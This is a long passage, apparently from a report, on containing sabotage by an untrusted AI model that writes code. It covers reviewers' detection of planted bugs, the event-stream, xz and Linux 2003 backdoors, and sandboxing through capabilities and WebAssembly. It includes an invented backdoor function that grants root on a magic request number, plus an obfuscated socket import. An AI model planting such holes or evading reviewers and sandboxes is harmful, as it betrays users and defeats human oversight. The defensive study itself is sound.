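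Other conditions made the task harder than it needed to be. The reviewers had four days to learn an unfamiliar program and no clean copy to compare with the altered one. For the public challenge, Wagner removed the part of the assurance document that contained the original code, because a comparison would have revealed the bug at once. A developer whose model edits existing software has the earlier version and can see exactly which lines are new. The marked region gave the Pvote reviewers similar help, so their task was roughly equivalent to reviewing a 100-line pull request from someone they had been told to distrust.

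These results show that experts can miss a deliberate bug in a short region of clean, simple code even when they suspect one and search for a long time, but it would be wrong to turn them into a detection rate. The two-line padded `total` is much easier to spot than Pvote's hard bug was, but an untrusted model wouldn't have to choose anything so obvious.

### AI models as reviewers

A developer who doesn't have 20 minutes to spend on each line may ask another AI model to do the reading. Models don't lose patience the way people do, and recent ones are good at finding accidental bugs. *(When) Should a Software Factory be Lights-off?* (Yang, He and colleagues, 2026) tested models on 1,000 pull requests from 98 open-source projects, each with a bug that people had later confirmed. The best model, Anthropic's Claude Opus 5, named the bug among its five most important comments in 71.9% of cases,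 compared with 47.7% for an Anthropic model from five months earlier.

The newer model did worse, scoring 64.2%, on the bugs that human reviewers had let through. Those bugs are the better guide to what a careful attacker would leave behind. In *CR-Bench-v2* (Pereira, Sinha and colleagues, 2026), the strongest systems scored only about a third. That collection starts from bugs that users reported in finished software, which may explain part of the gap, and the systems tested were different.

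Yang and colleagues found that AI reviewers were less likely to detect bugs in larger changes. An increase of one standard deviation in the logarithm of a change's length cut the odds of detection by about 41%, which supports Yee's decision to keep the program short. Detection did not differ significantly among the five programming languages they studied, which included Python and Rust, even though Rust's compiler is much stricter. Rust's compiler may well have kept some bugs out of the collection altogether, but the reviewers were not measurably better at finding the bugs that got past it.

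All these bugs were accidental. The most encouraging result for planted bugs comes from a DARPA contest. *AI Cyber Challenge marks pivotal inflection point for cyber defense* (DARPA, 2025) reports that the finalists' AI systems found 54 of the 63 vulnerabilities (86%) that the organisers had placed in real software, up from 37% in the semifinals a year earlier. That is the combined score of seven systems, so a single system would have found fewer. The contest also rewarded systems for proving that a vulnerability was real. This is harder for a bug that miscounts votes than for one that lets in an intruder, because people can observe an intrusion but can't recognise a wrong count unless they know the correct one.

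Attackers who try to avoid notice do considerably better. In *PRWeaver*, Wang, Cheng and Xie (2026) built 208 working attacks on ten real projects, nearly all of them in Python, and confirmed that each attack left the project's own tests passing. AI reviewers caught 50% to 60% of the attacks when they read one change at a time, but only 16% to 22% when they had to read a long run of changes together.

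AI reviewers share some of the weaknesses that the Pvote reviewers noticed in themselves. In *Words Speak Louder Than Code*, Shahriar, Cai and colleagues (2026) showed eight models the same code with different information about who had written it, and every model's verdicts shifted. Most were more lenient when the author sounded distinguished, but some were stricter. A warning made the models readier to call code vulnerable but no better at finding flaws, and they often failed to identify the actual vulnerability. Yang and colleagues also found cases in which a model believed a misleading comment or description. A developer can easily remove the author's name before an AI review, and can run the review both with and without the comments.

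Even an imperfect reviewer could be useful against a model that keeps trying. If the reviewer catches each planted bug with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance that *n* bugs all get through is

(1 − *p*)ⁿ.

With five bugs, the chance of missing all of them is about 1% if *p* = 0.6 and about 33% if *p* = 0.2. But assuming independence overstates the reviewer's chances, because a model that can tell which bugs are hard to find will plant only those. Pvote's expert reviewers did not find the hard bug during their review.

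Even a bug that is caught may not expose the model, because either altered version of `touch` could be an honest mistake, as could many one-line errors. A developer who finds one will probably fix it and give the model its next task. To recognise sabotage, the developer would have to keep a record of the model's mistakes and look for a pattern, such as rounding errors that always favour Northgate.

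## Three real attempts to plant malicious code, and what restrictions would have changed

Yee and Wagner planted their bugs as an exercise. In three well-documented cases, real attackers tried to get harmful code into widely used software: the JavaScript package event-stream in 2018, the compression library xz in 2024 and the Linux kernel in 2003. The harmful code needed different access in each case, so a restricted language would have helped much more in some cases than in others.

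### event-stream: a small function that needed no access

JavaScript is the language of web pages. JavaScript programmers build most of a program from *packages*, which other people publish on a registry called npm. Packages use other packages, so one application can contain hundreds or thousands. Each package that a program relies on, directly or indirectly, is a *dependency*. In ordinary JavaScript, every dependency has the same authority as the program.

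event-stream helps programs process data piece by piece. Arvanitis, Ntousakis and colleagues (2022), in *A Systematic Analysis of the Event-Stream Incident*, put its downloads at about two million a week. In the late summer of 2018 a stranger offered to help maintain it, and its creator handed over publishing rights. The new maintainer added a dependency called flatmap-stream, whose only job was to apply a function to each item in a stream and join the results. In October a new version of flatmap-stream brought in harmful code aimed at Copay, a Bitcoin wallet.

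The harmful code used authority on the developer's machine and in the finished wallet. When a Copay developer built a release, it wrote to the developer's disk to change a file in a barcode-reading package. In the finished wallet, the changed file read the customer's stored account data, replaced the function that returns private keys, and sent the keys over the network. It looked for accounts holding more than 100 Bitcoin or 1,000 Bitcoin Cash. Copay confirmed that it had shipped the code in versions 5.0.2 to 5.1.0, according to npm's *Details about the event-stream incident*.

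A developer working on an unrelated tool noticed an unexpected warning that some code was calling an outdated function. About three weeks later, another developer suspected an attack. npm removed flatmap-stream on 26 November, seven weeks after the harmful version appeared.

Of the three attacks, this one makes the strongest case for a restricted language. Joining lists requires no file or network access, so Joe-E's verifier would have rejected the harmful version for calling parts of the library that are not on the approved list. Arvanitis and colleagues think a tight sandbox around the single library would probably have worked too, but they doubt that one around the whole application would have, because the operating system cannot distinguish one package's actions from another's. They also think testing would have missed the attack, since it activated only in the real wallet. Fixing dependencies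 at known versions might only have delayed it.

Copay would have had to restrict its build tools as well as its wallet. If it had restricted only the wallet, the harmful code would have arrived inside the barcode package, with that package's permissions. A wallet needs packages that handle keys and packages that contact the network. If the attacker had taken over one that did both, they would have had all the necessary access from the start.

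### xz: harm that came in through the build

xz is a program for compressing files, and other programs use its library, liblzma. In March 2024 Andres Freund noticed that logging in to a test machine over ssh, the standard program for remote login, took about 0.8 seconds instead of 0.3. The search for the cause led to a backdoor in the two newest versions of xz, which Freund (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, reported to other developers on 29 March. Most Linux distributions had not yet adopted those versions outside their pre-releases.

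The ssh server does not use xz itself, but Debian and several other distributions modify it to report to systemd, the program that starts services, and systemd's library loads liblzma. This put the compression code in the same process as the code that decides who may log in. The library was written in C, which normally lets any code change memory anywhere in its process. The malicious code used this to redirect a function that the server calls when it checks a login key. Freund had not worked out exactly what the redirected function did, but thought it probably let an attacker get in or run commands.

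A decompressor needs as little authority as Joe-E's image decoder, since it takes bytes and returns bytes. A decompressor written in Joe-E, inside a server written in Joe-E, could not have redirected the login check. However, the attack used the *build script*, the commands that turn source code into a finished program, to add *native code*, which the processor runs directly. Joe-E's verifier does not check either of these. A build script can usually run any command on the machine, and native code is not bound by the source language's rules.

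A developer who compiles an untrusted model's source code, as Joe-E requires, must therefore also keep the model from editing the build script. If the model can change the build, it can put anything into the finished program, however strict the language is. The developer must also confine any essential native libraries separately, for example in WebAssembly sandboxes, which Firefox uses for some of its libraries.

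### The Linux kernel: a false check in privileged code

The kernel is the core of an operating system and controls what every other program may do. In 2003 the Linux developers kept the kernel's master copy in a system called BitKeeper, and a second copy in another system, CVS, for people who disliked BitKeeper. Somebody apparently broke into the CVS server and added two lines to `wait4`, a function that programs use to wait for something to happen. Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) explains that the lines looked like a check that rejects invalid requests, but they gave any program that made one particular invalid request the powers of *root*, the user who may do anything. The condition set the caller's user number to zero, which is root's number, instead of checking whether it was already zero.

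Every change in the master copy had a pointer to a record of its approval. Larry McVoy, whose company made BitKeeper, noticed that this change had no pointer and was not in the master copy. Another developer then asked on the mailing list whether the lines were an attempted backdoor. In *Re: BK2CVS problem*, McVoy (2003) agreed and said he had missed that.

A stricter language would have rejected the change as the attacker wrote it. Setting a number to zero produces a number, which C accepts as a condition. Java requires a condition to be true or false, so its compiler would have reported an error. As with Pvote's medium bug, an ordinary type check would have been better at catching the problem than a careful reader.

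Capabilities would have gone further. `wait4` has no need to change anyone's user number, but code in the kernel can reach the record of the current process without having received it, which is ambient authority. If `wait4` received a read-only view of that record, it could not make its caller root in any wording. An attacker would then have to change code that decides about permissions, and such code exists in every kernel. In an invented example, it might look like this:

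```java
static boolean mayActAsRoot(int user, int request) {
  return user == 0 || request == 7719;
}
```

This function receives two numbers and returns true or false. It is pure, and Joe-E would accept it. It holds no capability, yet the rest of the kernel gives out root's powers on its word, just as the firm's payment module pays whatever `total` returns. Ruling it out takes a specification:

mayActAsRoot(*u*, *r*) is true if and only if *u* = 0, for every *u* and *r*.

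In all three cases, somebody noticed a symptom before anyone had read and understood the harmful lines. Two of the symptoms, the warning and the slow logins, came from mistakes that a more careful attacker would avoid. The third, the missing approval record, came to light because of a rule the Linux developers had set up. A developer can apply the same rule to a model by letting it change the code only through a process that records who approved what.

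### Hardened JavaScript and LavaMoat

Few teams will rewrite a working application in Joe-E, so researchers and companies have looked for ways to add limits to languages already in use. One of these approaches, Hardened JavaScript, has two main parts. `lockdown` freezes the language's built-in objects, such as arrays and text, so that one package cannot change how they behave for all the others. `Compartment` runs code with its own global variables, and whoever creates the compartment chooses those variables.

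LavaMoat, a set of tools made by the wallet company MetaMask, uses Hardened JavaScript to give every dependency its own compartment. Packages LavaMoat runs this way share no references unless other code passes them in or a policy file allows it. The policy names the global variables, system functions and other packages that each one may use. For chalk, a popular package for colouring text, the entry is short:

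```json
"chalk": {
  "globals": {
    "navigator.userAgent": true,
    "navigator.userAgentData": true
  }
}
```

chalk may read two descriptions of the user's browser and can reach neither the network nor the disk.

In September 2025, attackers put code designed to steal from cryptocurrency wallets into more than 18 npm packages, including chalk, and developers downloaded the bad versions over 2.5 million times, according to Datadog Security Labs' *Learnings from recent npm compromises*. The code replaced `fetch`, the browser's function for network requests, and swapped the attackers' addresses into payments. The attackers made only $500 to $1,000. In *How to survive supply-chain attacks*, Obici ran the malicious chalk under LavaMoat with the policy shown above, which came from the last clean version. The code failed with an error as soon as it tried to replace `fetch`.

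That was one sample, and nothing suggests that its author had prepared for LavaMoat. Obici's firm, OtterSec, had audited one of LavaMoat's components in late 2024 and found ways to get past its protection. A determined attacker, or a model that knows which tool is in use, would look for such flaws.

Some attacks finish before the limits take effect. Later in September 2025, a program called Shai-Hulud spread itself through npm. It stole developers' passwords and access tokens, then used them to publish infected versions of those developers' other packages, according to the security research team Unit 42 (2025). WASOC's *NPM Supply Chain Compromise Activity* (2025), a government advisory from Western Australia, reports that a new variant in November stole them while the package was still installing. A compartment confines a package only when the program runs, so it could not have stopped this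 theft. LavaMoat has a separate tool that turns off all installation scripts except those the developer lists. As with xz, a team that restricts only the running program leaves attackers an easier way in.

A rough calculation shows how much separate permissions can help. Suppose an application has 1,000 dependencies, and attackers take over each one with a probability of 1 in 10,000 a year. The chance that they get at least one is

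1 − 0.9999¹⁰⁰⁰ ≈ 9.5%.

Without compartments, any one of them gives the attackers the network. If the policy allows only 50 packages to use it, the chance of getting one of those is

1 − 0.9999⁵⁰ ≈ 0.5%.

The real benefit is smaller, because attackers choose their targets and would go after the 50.

### Who looks after the policy file

Writing a policy by hand for a thousand dependencies would be tedious, so LavaMoat reads the code of every package and generates a file listing what each one currently uses. The application's developers then review it and put their corrections in a second file, which takes precedence. LavaMoat's *Using Policies* recommends a manual review whenever the generated file changes, and gives the example of a text-formatting package that turns out to write files. This review is worthwhile because one new line in a policy is much easier to notice than a few bad lines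 in a large package.

The same convenience creates a risk, because the generated policy records what the packages do, whether or not they should. Obici warns that if a developer regenerates the policy while a malicious version is installed, it may grant the malware the access it needs. A policy would not have protected a Copay developer who regenerated it in October 2018 and accepted it without reading it.

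An untrusted model should not be able to edit or regenerate the policy, since it could then set its own permissions. The policy also covers only dependencies, so LavaMoat leaves the application's own code unrestricted. If a model writes `total` directly into the accounting program, the function can access everything the program can. To restrict it, the firm would have to keep `total` in a separate package, with its own policy entry that grants no permissions.

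Keeping packages compatible also takes work. A JavaScript program can work out a function's name while it runs, so the generator sometimes misses a permission that a package needs, and the package fails until somebody adds it. Packages that alter built-in objects stop working after `lockdown`. According to the Hardened JavaScript package's npm page, compartments also disable the usual functions for random numbers and the current time, which makes code more predictable but can break packages that rely on them. *NodeShield* (2025) presents a rival permission system for server-side JavaScript that aims for shorter policies and fewer such failures, with what it calls "minimal overhead".

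Java had a similar facility, the Security Manager, for many years. Its developers eventually deprecated it, partly because working out suitable policies was a "practically insurmountable challenge".

### Gradient: moving to capabilities one library at a time

Capability languages don't need separate policy files because the program's structure determines which code can use what. But they require every part of a program, including its libraries, to do without ambient authority. Boruch-Gruszecki, Ghosn and colleagues (2024), in *Gradient*, argue that this is probably why industry hardly uses them. Gradient is an experimental extension of Scala that lets a team convert one library at a time while still restricting the unconverted ones.

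| State of the library | How Gradient limits it | When a violation appears |
|---|---|---|
| Unchanged, and possibly native code | The caller wraps it in an `enclosed` block, which the processor helps to enforce | While the program runs |
| Same structure, with capabilities added to its types | The caller can wrap it in a `restricted` block | At compile time |
| Rewritten to receive its capabilities as arguments | It has only what its caller passes in | At compile time |

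Suppose the accounting firm saves its invoices with a library that should use the disk and nothing else. With the file system as `fs`, the firm would write one of these lines:

```scala
enclosed [{fs}] { OldArchive.save(invoices) }
restricted [{fs}] { Archive.save(invoices) }
```

If the old library tries to open a network connection, the program stops with an error. If the newer library contains code that would open a connection, the program does not compile. The compiler also rejects any call to an unconverted library outside an `enclosed` block, so a developer cannot omit the protection by mistake.

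The types are most useful when a library changes. If an update to a fully converted logging library needs the network for the first time, it has to require a network capability, and every program that uses it stops compiling until a developer decides to provide one. The October version of flatmap-stream would have needed disk access, so event-stream would not have compiled with it, even if nobody had suspected anything.

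Gradient also limits how long code can keep a capability. Boruch-Gruszecki and colleagues give the example of a text-recognition library that needs the network once, to download an update, and later reads private documents. In most languages, it could store the connection during the update and use it later to send the documents out. Gradient's types prevent the library from retrieving the stored connection after the update.

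To find out how much work a conversion takes, the team added capability types to Scala's standard XML library. They changed about 260 of its 4,200 lines, or 6%, and around 200 of those changes added only a few characters. They did not have to restructure anything. However, this brought the library only to the middle row of the table, and they expect that a full conversion could need major restructuring of the library and the programs that use it. The library also makes little use of the disk or the network, so converting one that manages files or connections would probably take more work.

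Types don't slow a program down while it runs, but `enclosed` blocks do. Gradient relies on *Enclosures* for these blocks, an earlier system that uses features of Intel processors to block access to memory and to system calls (requests to the operating system). In the best case, Enclosures slowed a realistic application by only 2%. The team estimated Gradient's slowdown by counting the slow operations in a test program and multiplying by times measured for Enclosures. More than 90% of the estimated slowdown came from reading many small files inside an `enclosed` block. The program would run at almost its normal speed with one of the two Intel features, but the other made each system call much slower.

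In a presentation of Gradient, Boruch-Gruszecki and colleagues name the xz backdoor as an example of the attacks that worry them. Gradient's `enclosed` block could confine a native compression library, which Joe-E cannot do, but it might still have failed against this attack. The harmful code in xz ran while the ssh server was starting up and loading its libraries, so a block that began when the server first called the library would have begun too late. Gradient would also need a trustworthy build, since a hostile build script could remove the block. The design is young, though Aebi has since built a language on the same principle (*Implementation of a gradually compartmentalized programming language*, 2025).

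### Working out what a tool does from its code

AI agents use another kind of code from strangers, called *tools*, which are small programs that do things like write a file or search the web. An agent chooses a tool by reading its description, which can leave things out. *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a tool that writes a file, as described, but also reports usage figures to an outside server. The paper's system ignores the description and analyses the tool's code.

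The analysis follows every path through a tool and lists the effects it could have, along with the inputs that might influence them. The list is called a *synopsis*. For the uploading version of `total`, it would contain a line like this:

```text
input(invoices) -> effect(net:write)
```

The honest version would have an empty synopsis, and so would the version that pads Northgate's bills.

A synopsis can show that a tool writes files, but not which ones, because the file name arrives only when the agent calls the tool. The system therefore relies on the tool's developer to put a small sandbox around each such operation. The agent's side sends limits with each call, such as a permitted folder, and the sandbox enforces them. A second analysis confirms that the developer has wrapped every operation and that the tool does not tamper with the limits.

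Adam and colleagues tested a prototype on three situations from a programmer's work, each with a harmless and a harmful variant. In one, the agent publishes a project that may or may not contain a secret key. They replayed recorded sessions to test each method on the same requests.

| Method | Harmless variants allowed | Harmful variants blocked |
|---|---|---|
| No protection | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
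| One fixed sandbox around all tools | 2 of 3 | 1 of 3 |
| Synopsis alone | 2 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
| Synopsis with small sandboxes | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

The fixed sandbox did worst because the same action, such as sending a project to a public site, can be fine on one occasion and a leak on another. But the system's own designers chose the six cases, so the cases are only a demonstration and can't show how often the system would fail. Adam and colleagues also did not measure how much the checks slow a tool down.

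The system is also designed to protect against careless or confused tool developers and a model that requests the wrong action, which are milder threats than an untrusted model. The prototype analyses only Rust, whose strict types make effects easier to trace. Adam and colleagues expect Python and JavaScript to be much harder to analyse, with more false alarms. The analysis also stops wherever a tool passes work to a shell command, a database or a website. In those cases, the system has to rely on its sandboxes or refuse the call.

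The policy is again the hardest part to supply. The prototype assumes a source that always knows what the user wants and whether the data are sensitive. In practice, users could write the rules themselves, which Adam and colleagues consider laborious, or a second AI model could write them from the user's request. A mistake by that model, like a careless line in a LavaMoat policy, would let the secret key through even though the sandbox worked correctly.

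## WebAssembly: sandboxed libraries in Firefox and sandboxed code from models

Like Gradient's `enclosed` blocks and the small sandboxes around AI tools, WebAssembly confines code whose own language sets few limits, and it works on almost any computer. Browser makers designed this low-level format for web pages, and compilers can produce it from C, Rust and many other languages. Programmers can keep the language they know because the limits apply to the compiled program. Mozilla uses WebAssembly to confine C libraries inside Firefox, and some developers now use it to run Python written by AI models.

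### How the format confines a program

A compiler turns source code into a *module*, a file of compact instructions for an imaginary processor. The *host* is the program that uses the module, such as a browser or the firm's accounting software. It gives the module to a WebAssembly runtime, which checks the instructions and translates them for the real processor. Here is `total` in WebAssembly's text form:

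```wat
(module
  (memory (export "memory") 1)
  (func (export "total") (param $at i32) (param $end i32) (result i64)
    (local $sum i64)
    (block $done
      (loop $next
        (br_if $done (i32.ge_u (local.get $at) (local.get $end)))
        (local.set $sum
          (i64.add (local.get $sum) (i64.load (local.get $at))))
        (local.set $at (i32.add (local.get $at) (i32.const 8)))
        (br $next)))
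    (local.get $sum)))
```

The host writes the amounts into the module's memory, eight bytes each, and calls `total` with the positions where the list starts and ends. The loop adds one amount at a time until it reaches the end.

Before anything runs, a *validator* checks the types of all the instructions. Addition, for example, takes two 64-bit whole numbers and produces one:

i64.add : [i64 i64] → [i64].

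If one of the two inputs were a 32-bit number, the validator would reject the whole module.

The instruction `i64.load` reads eight bytes from the module's *linear memory*, a row of bytes numbered from zero. If the memory has *m* bytes, a read at position *a* succeeds only when *a* + 8 ≤ *m*. Otherwise the runtime stops the program. Positions refer only to bytes in linear memory, so the module can't reach the host's data by computing a different position.

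WebAssembly also has *structured control flow*: `br` and `br_if` can jump only to the start of an enclosing loop or the end of an enclosing block. A module's instructions are stored outside its linear memory, so it can't rewrite its own code or run its data as code. These limits would have kept a compression library like xz's from redirecting the ssh server's functions, provided that no one had tampered with the build.

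No instruction opens a file or reads the clock. A module can affect the outside world only through its *imports*, which are functions that the host supplies. The module above has none, so it can only compute and change its own memory. If the firm wants a log of invoice counts, it can supply one function, and the module declares it like this:

```wat
(import "log" "count" (func $count (param i32)))
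```

This is the same narrow channel as Joe-E's `Counter`, and a reviewer can learn as much from the import list as from a list of received capabilities. But WebAssembly's limits are coarser, because all the functions in a module share its memory and imports, whereas two objects in one Joe-E program can have different capabilities. To isolate two libraries from each other, the host has to put them in separate modules.

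### Handing over a folder or a connection

Most programs need some files, and it would be tedious if every host invented its own functions for them. WASI, the WebAssembly System Interface, is a standard set of functions for files, clocks, network connections and similar resources. The host opens certain folders before the program starts and gives the program a handle to each one. With Wasmtime, a popular runtime for use outside browsers, the firm could write:

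```sh
wasmtime run --dir invoices report.wasm
```

The program can then open files inside `invoices` and no others. Its handle is a number that selects an entry in a table the runtime keeps for this program. Code could easily guess another number, but it would reach only what is already in that table. Dennis and Van Horn's 1966 capability lists worked in much the same way.

The *component model* builds on this. A plain module can exchange only numbers with its host, so the two sides have to agree on how a list of invoices looks as bytes. A component can exchange text, lists, records and handles, and it describes them in an interface:

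```wit
package firm:accounts;

interface totals {
  record invoice {
    supplier: string,
    customer: string,
    pence: s64,
  }
  total: func(invoices: list<invoice>) -> s64;
}

world totaller {
  export totals;
}
```

The `world` lists what the component provides and what it imports. This component imports nothing. The runtime copies the invoices into the component's own memory, so the component cannot read the caller's memory. Compilers sometimes add imports, such as a clock, so the firm should check the list of imports in the compiled component as well as the interface that the model wrote.

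By autumn 2026 Wasmtime contained three generations of WASI. The second introduced the component model, and the third added streams of data and calls that run in the background. stack.watch's *Bytecodealliance Bytecodealliance* lists known flaws in software from the Bytecode Alliance, the group behind Wasmtime. The third generation is still young, and its entries in that list begin with Wasmtime version 46, while version 50 was out by October. Many of the autumn's entries concern the third generation or the component model. A firm that needs only a function from numbers to numbers can avoid these flaws by using a plain module.

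### Firefox checks what its libraries return

Firefox uses dozens of third-party libraries to decode images, sound and fonts. Nearly all are written in C, and attackers regularly find bugs in them. An attacker can use a malicious audio file to take over the renderer, the part of the browser that handles the page, and then read the user's email if the page is a mail site. *Retrofitting Fine Grain Isolation in the Firefox Renderer* (Narayan, Disselkoen and colleagues, 2020) describes RLBox, a tool for sandboxing such libraries.

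Barth's objection to the DarpaBrowser is weak here, because RLBox sandboxes single libraries that need very little access. Like Joe-E's decoder, a hostile image library in its own sandbox can do little more than show the wrong picture.

Even so, the sandbox alone does not protect Firefox. Suppose the JPEG library reports which row of the picture it has finished, and Firefox decides where to put the pixels from that number without checking it. If a hostile library reports row 5,000,000 of a 400-row picture, Firefox will write outside the picture and damage its own memory, even though the library never left its sandbox.

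RLBox therefore gives everything that comes out of a sandbox a special type, `tainted`. In simplified form, the code in Firefox looks like this:

```cpp
tainted<int> row = sandbox_invoke(library, current_row);

picture[row] = pixels;            // the compiler rejects this line

int safe = row.verify([&](int r) {
  if (r < 0 || r >= height) stop_decoding();
  return r;
});
picture[safe] = pixels;
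```

A tainted number takes up no more space than an ordinary one. If Firefox adds something to it, the result is tainted too. Firefox can't use it to choose between two branches or to pick a place in its own memory until a programmer has written a check. The check can enforce what the library's manual promises, as above, or it can protect the memory directly. For a picture stored as one long buffer, the second kind of check would be

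0 ≤ *row* × *width* ≤ *buffer size* − *row size*,

which leaves room for at least one more row.

Some tainted data is in memory that both Firefox and the library can change, so a hostile library could alter a number after Firefox checks it but before Firefox uses it. RLBox requires the programmer to copy such data out of the shared memory first, and the compiler reports an error if the programmer forgets. RLBox also limits which Firefox functions the library may call, and Firefox can withdraw that permission when a job is done. Narayan and colleagues say they made many such mistakes when they worked by hand, and found a good number only after RLBox flagged them.

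The conversion took one to three days for each library that they timed:

| Library and its job | Working days | Lines of Firefox code around it, before and after | Different checks written |
|---|---|---|---|
| zlib, compressed pages | 1 | 649 → 757 | 3 |
| libvorbis, sound | 2 | 328 → 395 | 2 |
| libtheora, video | 3 | 220 → 297 | 3 |
| libvpx, video | 3 | 286 → 368 | 2 |
| libjpeg, images | not timed | 720 → 1,058 | 11 |
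| libpng, images | not timed | 847 → 1,317 | 14 |

RLBox found 100 places where Firefox relied on a value from one of these libraries, and 35 short checks covered them all. Writing the checks was the hardest part, because the programmer has to know which values make sense. The people who did this work had also built RLBox, so others might need longer.

Their prototype slowed page loading by 3% and raised peak memory use by 25%, but it used Native Client, an older sandbox that Google has since abandoned in favour of WebAssembly. The first library to reach users in a WebAssembly sandbox was libGraphite, which arranges the letters of certain rare fonts. It shipped in Firefox 74 for Linux and Firefox 75 for Mac. In a demanding test, libGraphite's code ran 85% slower and Firefox's font rendering 50% slower, while peak memory use rose by less than 1%. Narayan and colleagues attribute the slowdown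 to the compilers, which were then new, and say users can't notice it because loading a page mostly means waiting for the network and for images.

Firefox uses many small sandboxes because if all the libraries shared one, an attacker who broke the sound decoder could also control zlib, which unpacks the scripts of web pages. The prototype had a separate sandbox for each combination of library, website and kind of content, and Firefox creates a new one for every Graphite font. The accounting firm could copy this by starting `total` in a new sandbox every night, so that the function couldn't keep data from the night before.

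RLBox protects a host from a hostile library only if the host's own code is trustworthy. A model that wrote the host's code could strip the taint from a value with a C++ cast or with RLBox's `unsafeUnverified()` function, which removes it without any check. That function is useful when code is only partly converted to RLBox and for data such as pixels, where any value is harmless. An untrusted model can therefore write the library, but somebody else must write the checks.

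The checks are also weak for a function like `total`. The firm can check that the sum is positive and not absurdly large, but a sum with 2% added to Northgate's bills will pass. To catch the padding, the check would have to add up the invoices itself, and then the firm would not need the model's function. Checks work better for a task like sorting invoices, because the host can easily confirm that the result is in order and contains the same invoices.

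### Ordinary Python from a model

In Firefox, programmers had to change the code around each library, but a developer who wants to run short scripts from a model can restrict only the runtime and let the model write ordinary Python. Simon Willison, who makes Datasette, a program for exploring databases, built such a sandbox in June 2026. Datasette's plug-ins run with all of its privileges, so a bad one can break the program or leak private data. *Running Python code in a sandbox with MicroPython and WASM* (Willison, 2026) describes his goal of running such code, including code from Datasette's AI agent, with strict limits on files, network, memory and computing time.

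Python is awkward to translate directly into WebAssembly because a Python program can create new code while it runs. The usual solution is to compile a Python interpreter to WebAssembly and give it the program as text. Willison chose MicroPython, a small version of Python for tiny devices, and had OpenAI's coding agent Codex do most of the work. The resulting module is 362 kilobytes and includes 78 lines of new C that let Python code call functions the host provides.

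The firm could run a model's `total` roughly like this:

```python
with MicroPythonSession() as session:
    session.run(invoice_data)     # the firm's text: creates the list
    session.run(model_code)       # the model's text: defines total
    answer = session.run("print(total(invoices))").stdout
```

If the firm provides no network function, the version of the script that uploads data fails. Disguising the import as `__import__("soc" + "ket")` doesn't help, because the code has no way to open a connection. The model doesn't need to learn a new language, and nobody has to read the script before it runs. But the model's code controls the text in `answer`, so the firm should treat it as tainted and accept only a number.

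Variables normally vanish when the interpreter stops, which would be inconvenient for an agent that works in small steps. Willison keeps the interpreter running and has it call a host function that waits until the next piece of code is ready. Wasmtime limits memory directly and limits computing time with *fuel*, a budget that shrinks with each operation. The program stops when the fuel runs out. Willison set the budget at 20 million units but is not sure that this is the right amount. Fuel also limits how long a function can stall to send a signal by timing. The firm could also hold back every answer until a fixed time has passed, so that an observer learns only whether the function finished.

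Willison challenged GPT-5.5 to break out of the sandbox, and it failed. This is weak evidence because the test was informal and used only one model. Willison calls the package an alpha version and does not recommend it to anyone unwilling to take "a significant risk". Part of the package runs outside the sandbox and sets its limits, so it belongs to the trusted computing base. An AI model wrote that part, which is a problem for a developer who distrusts the model. Willison (2026) also has a complete WebAssembly engine, pwasm, that models wrote in plain Python. By October it could run MicroPython too, but Willison "wouldn't trust this thing at all". A firm should be as cautious about any sandbox that an untrusted model has written for itself.

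MicroPython's small library is enough for a script that totals invoices, but a coding agent needs compilers, test programs and a command line. *External sandboxes for coding agents* (Willison, 2026) runs a whole Linux system inside WebAssembly on a simulated processor. The agent, such as Claude Code or Codex, stays outside and sends in commands, which can use only the folders the user has chosen and have no network access by default. The user can allow particular websites through a proxy, a go-between that adds passwords and access keys to requests after they leave the sandbox, so the agent can use a key without being able to read it.

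Willison favors a sandbox because it does not depend on a model's judgment, and because people who must approve every action soon approve everything without thinking. The Pvote reviewers had a similar problem with fatigue. However, the sandbox covers only action code, not the code that the agent delivers in the project folder.

Large companies run other people's code in WebAssembly too. The Hacker News' *Two Critical Wasmtime Flaws Could Let Malicious WebAssembly Modules Escape Sandboxes* (2026) names Fastly, whose Compute service runs customers' programs on Wasmtime. Akamai sells a WebAssembly sandbox specifically for AI agents and the code they write. Akamai says customers who deploy a WebAssembly application there can list the hosts, databases and files it may use.

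Cloudflare's *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster* describes a service that runs agents' code in isolates, which are separate JavaScript environments that start very quickly. The service can also run WebAssembly and Python, but Cloudflare recommends JavaScript because short snippets load and run much faster in it. *Cloudflare says containers are too slow for AI agent sandboxing* adds that a second sandbox surrounds the first, and that developers can inspect, change or block each outgoing request.

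### Harm inside the rules

Suppose the firm lets an agent's script read the client folder and contact the bank. The script reads what each customer owes and puts it in the reference line of a payment. The runtime checks the read and the connection and allows both, although the firm never meant to send this data to the payee. Permission to read a file and permission to send data to a host do not imply permission to send that file to that host, but a sandbox that checks each call on its own can't enforce this distinction.

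The firm can split the job between two sandboxes. The first can read the client folder but has no network access, and may return only an amount and an account number. The host checks these two values and passes them to the second, which can contact the bank but has no files. This leaves a much smaller channel for leaks. The split works when the firm knows in advance what has to pass between the sandboxes, but it often doesn't when an agent's task is loosely worded. Odersky and colleagues' system for agents is meant to be more flexible, and tracks confidential data in the types.

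The sandbox also doesn't catch memory errors that stay inside it. Suppose a C version of `total` copies each supplier's name into 32 bytes of memory, with the running sum stored right after them. A longer name will overwrite the sum. In an ordinary process, an attacker might use such a bug to take over the accounting program, and WebAssembly prevents that. But the overwrite stays within the module's own memory, so the runtime doesn't stop it, and the firm gets a wrong total. A supplier who knew about the bug could choose a name that produces the total they want. An untrusted model could plant the bug, and it would look like one of the most common errors in C.

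For this reason, Willison is slightly too optimistic about the 78 lines of C in the MicroPython package. He is not a C programmer. He had two models explain the code and reasoned that the worst result of a serious flaw would be a failed run. Such a flaw could also corrupt the interpreter's data and give a wrong answer with no error.

### Flaws in the runtimes

All these limits depend on the runtime, and people found far more flaws in runtimes in 2026 than before. stack.watch lists five to eight a year in the Bytecode Alliance's software from 2021 to 2025, and 65 in 2026 by mid-November. The total apparently includes both Wasmtime and WAMR, a small runtime for devices. Many of the recent entries describe ways to crash the host or exhaust its memory, but a few of the flaws could have let hostile code escape the sandbox.

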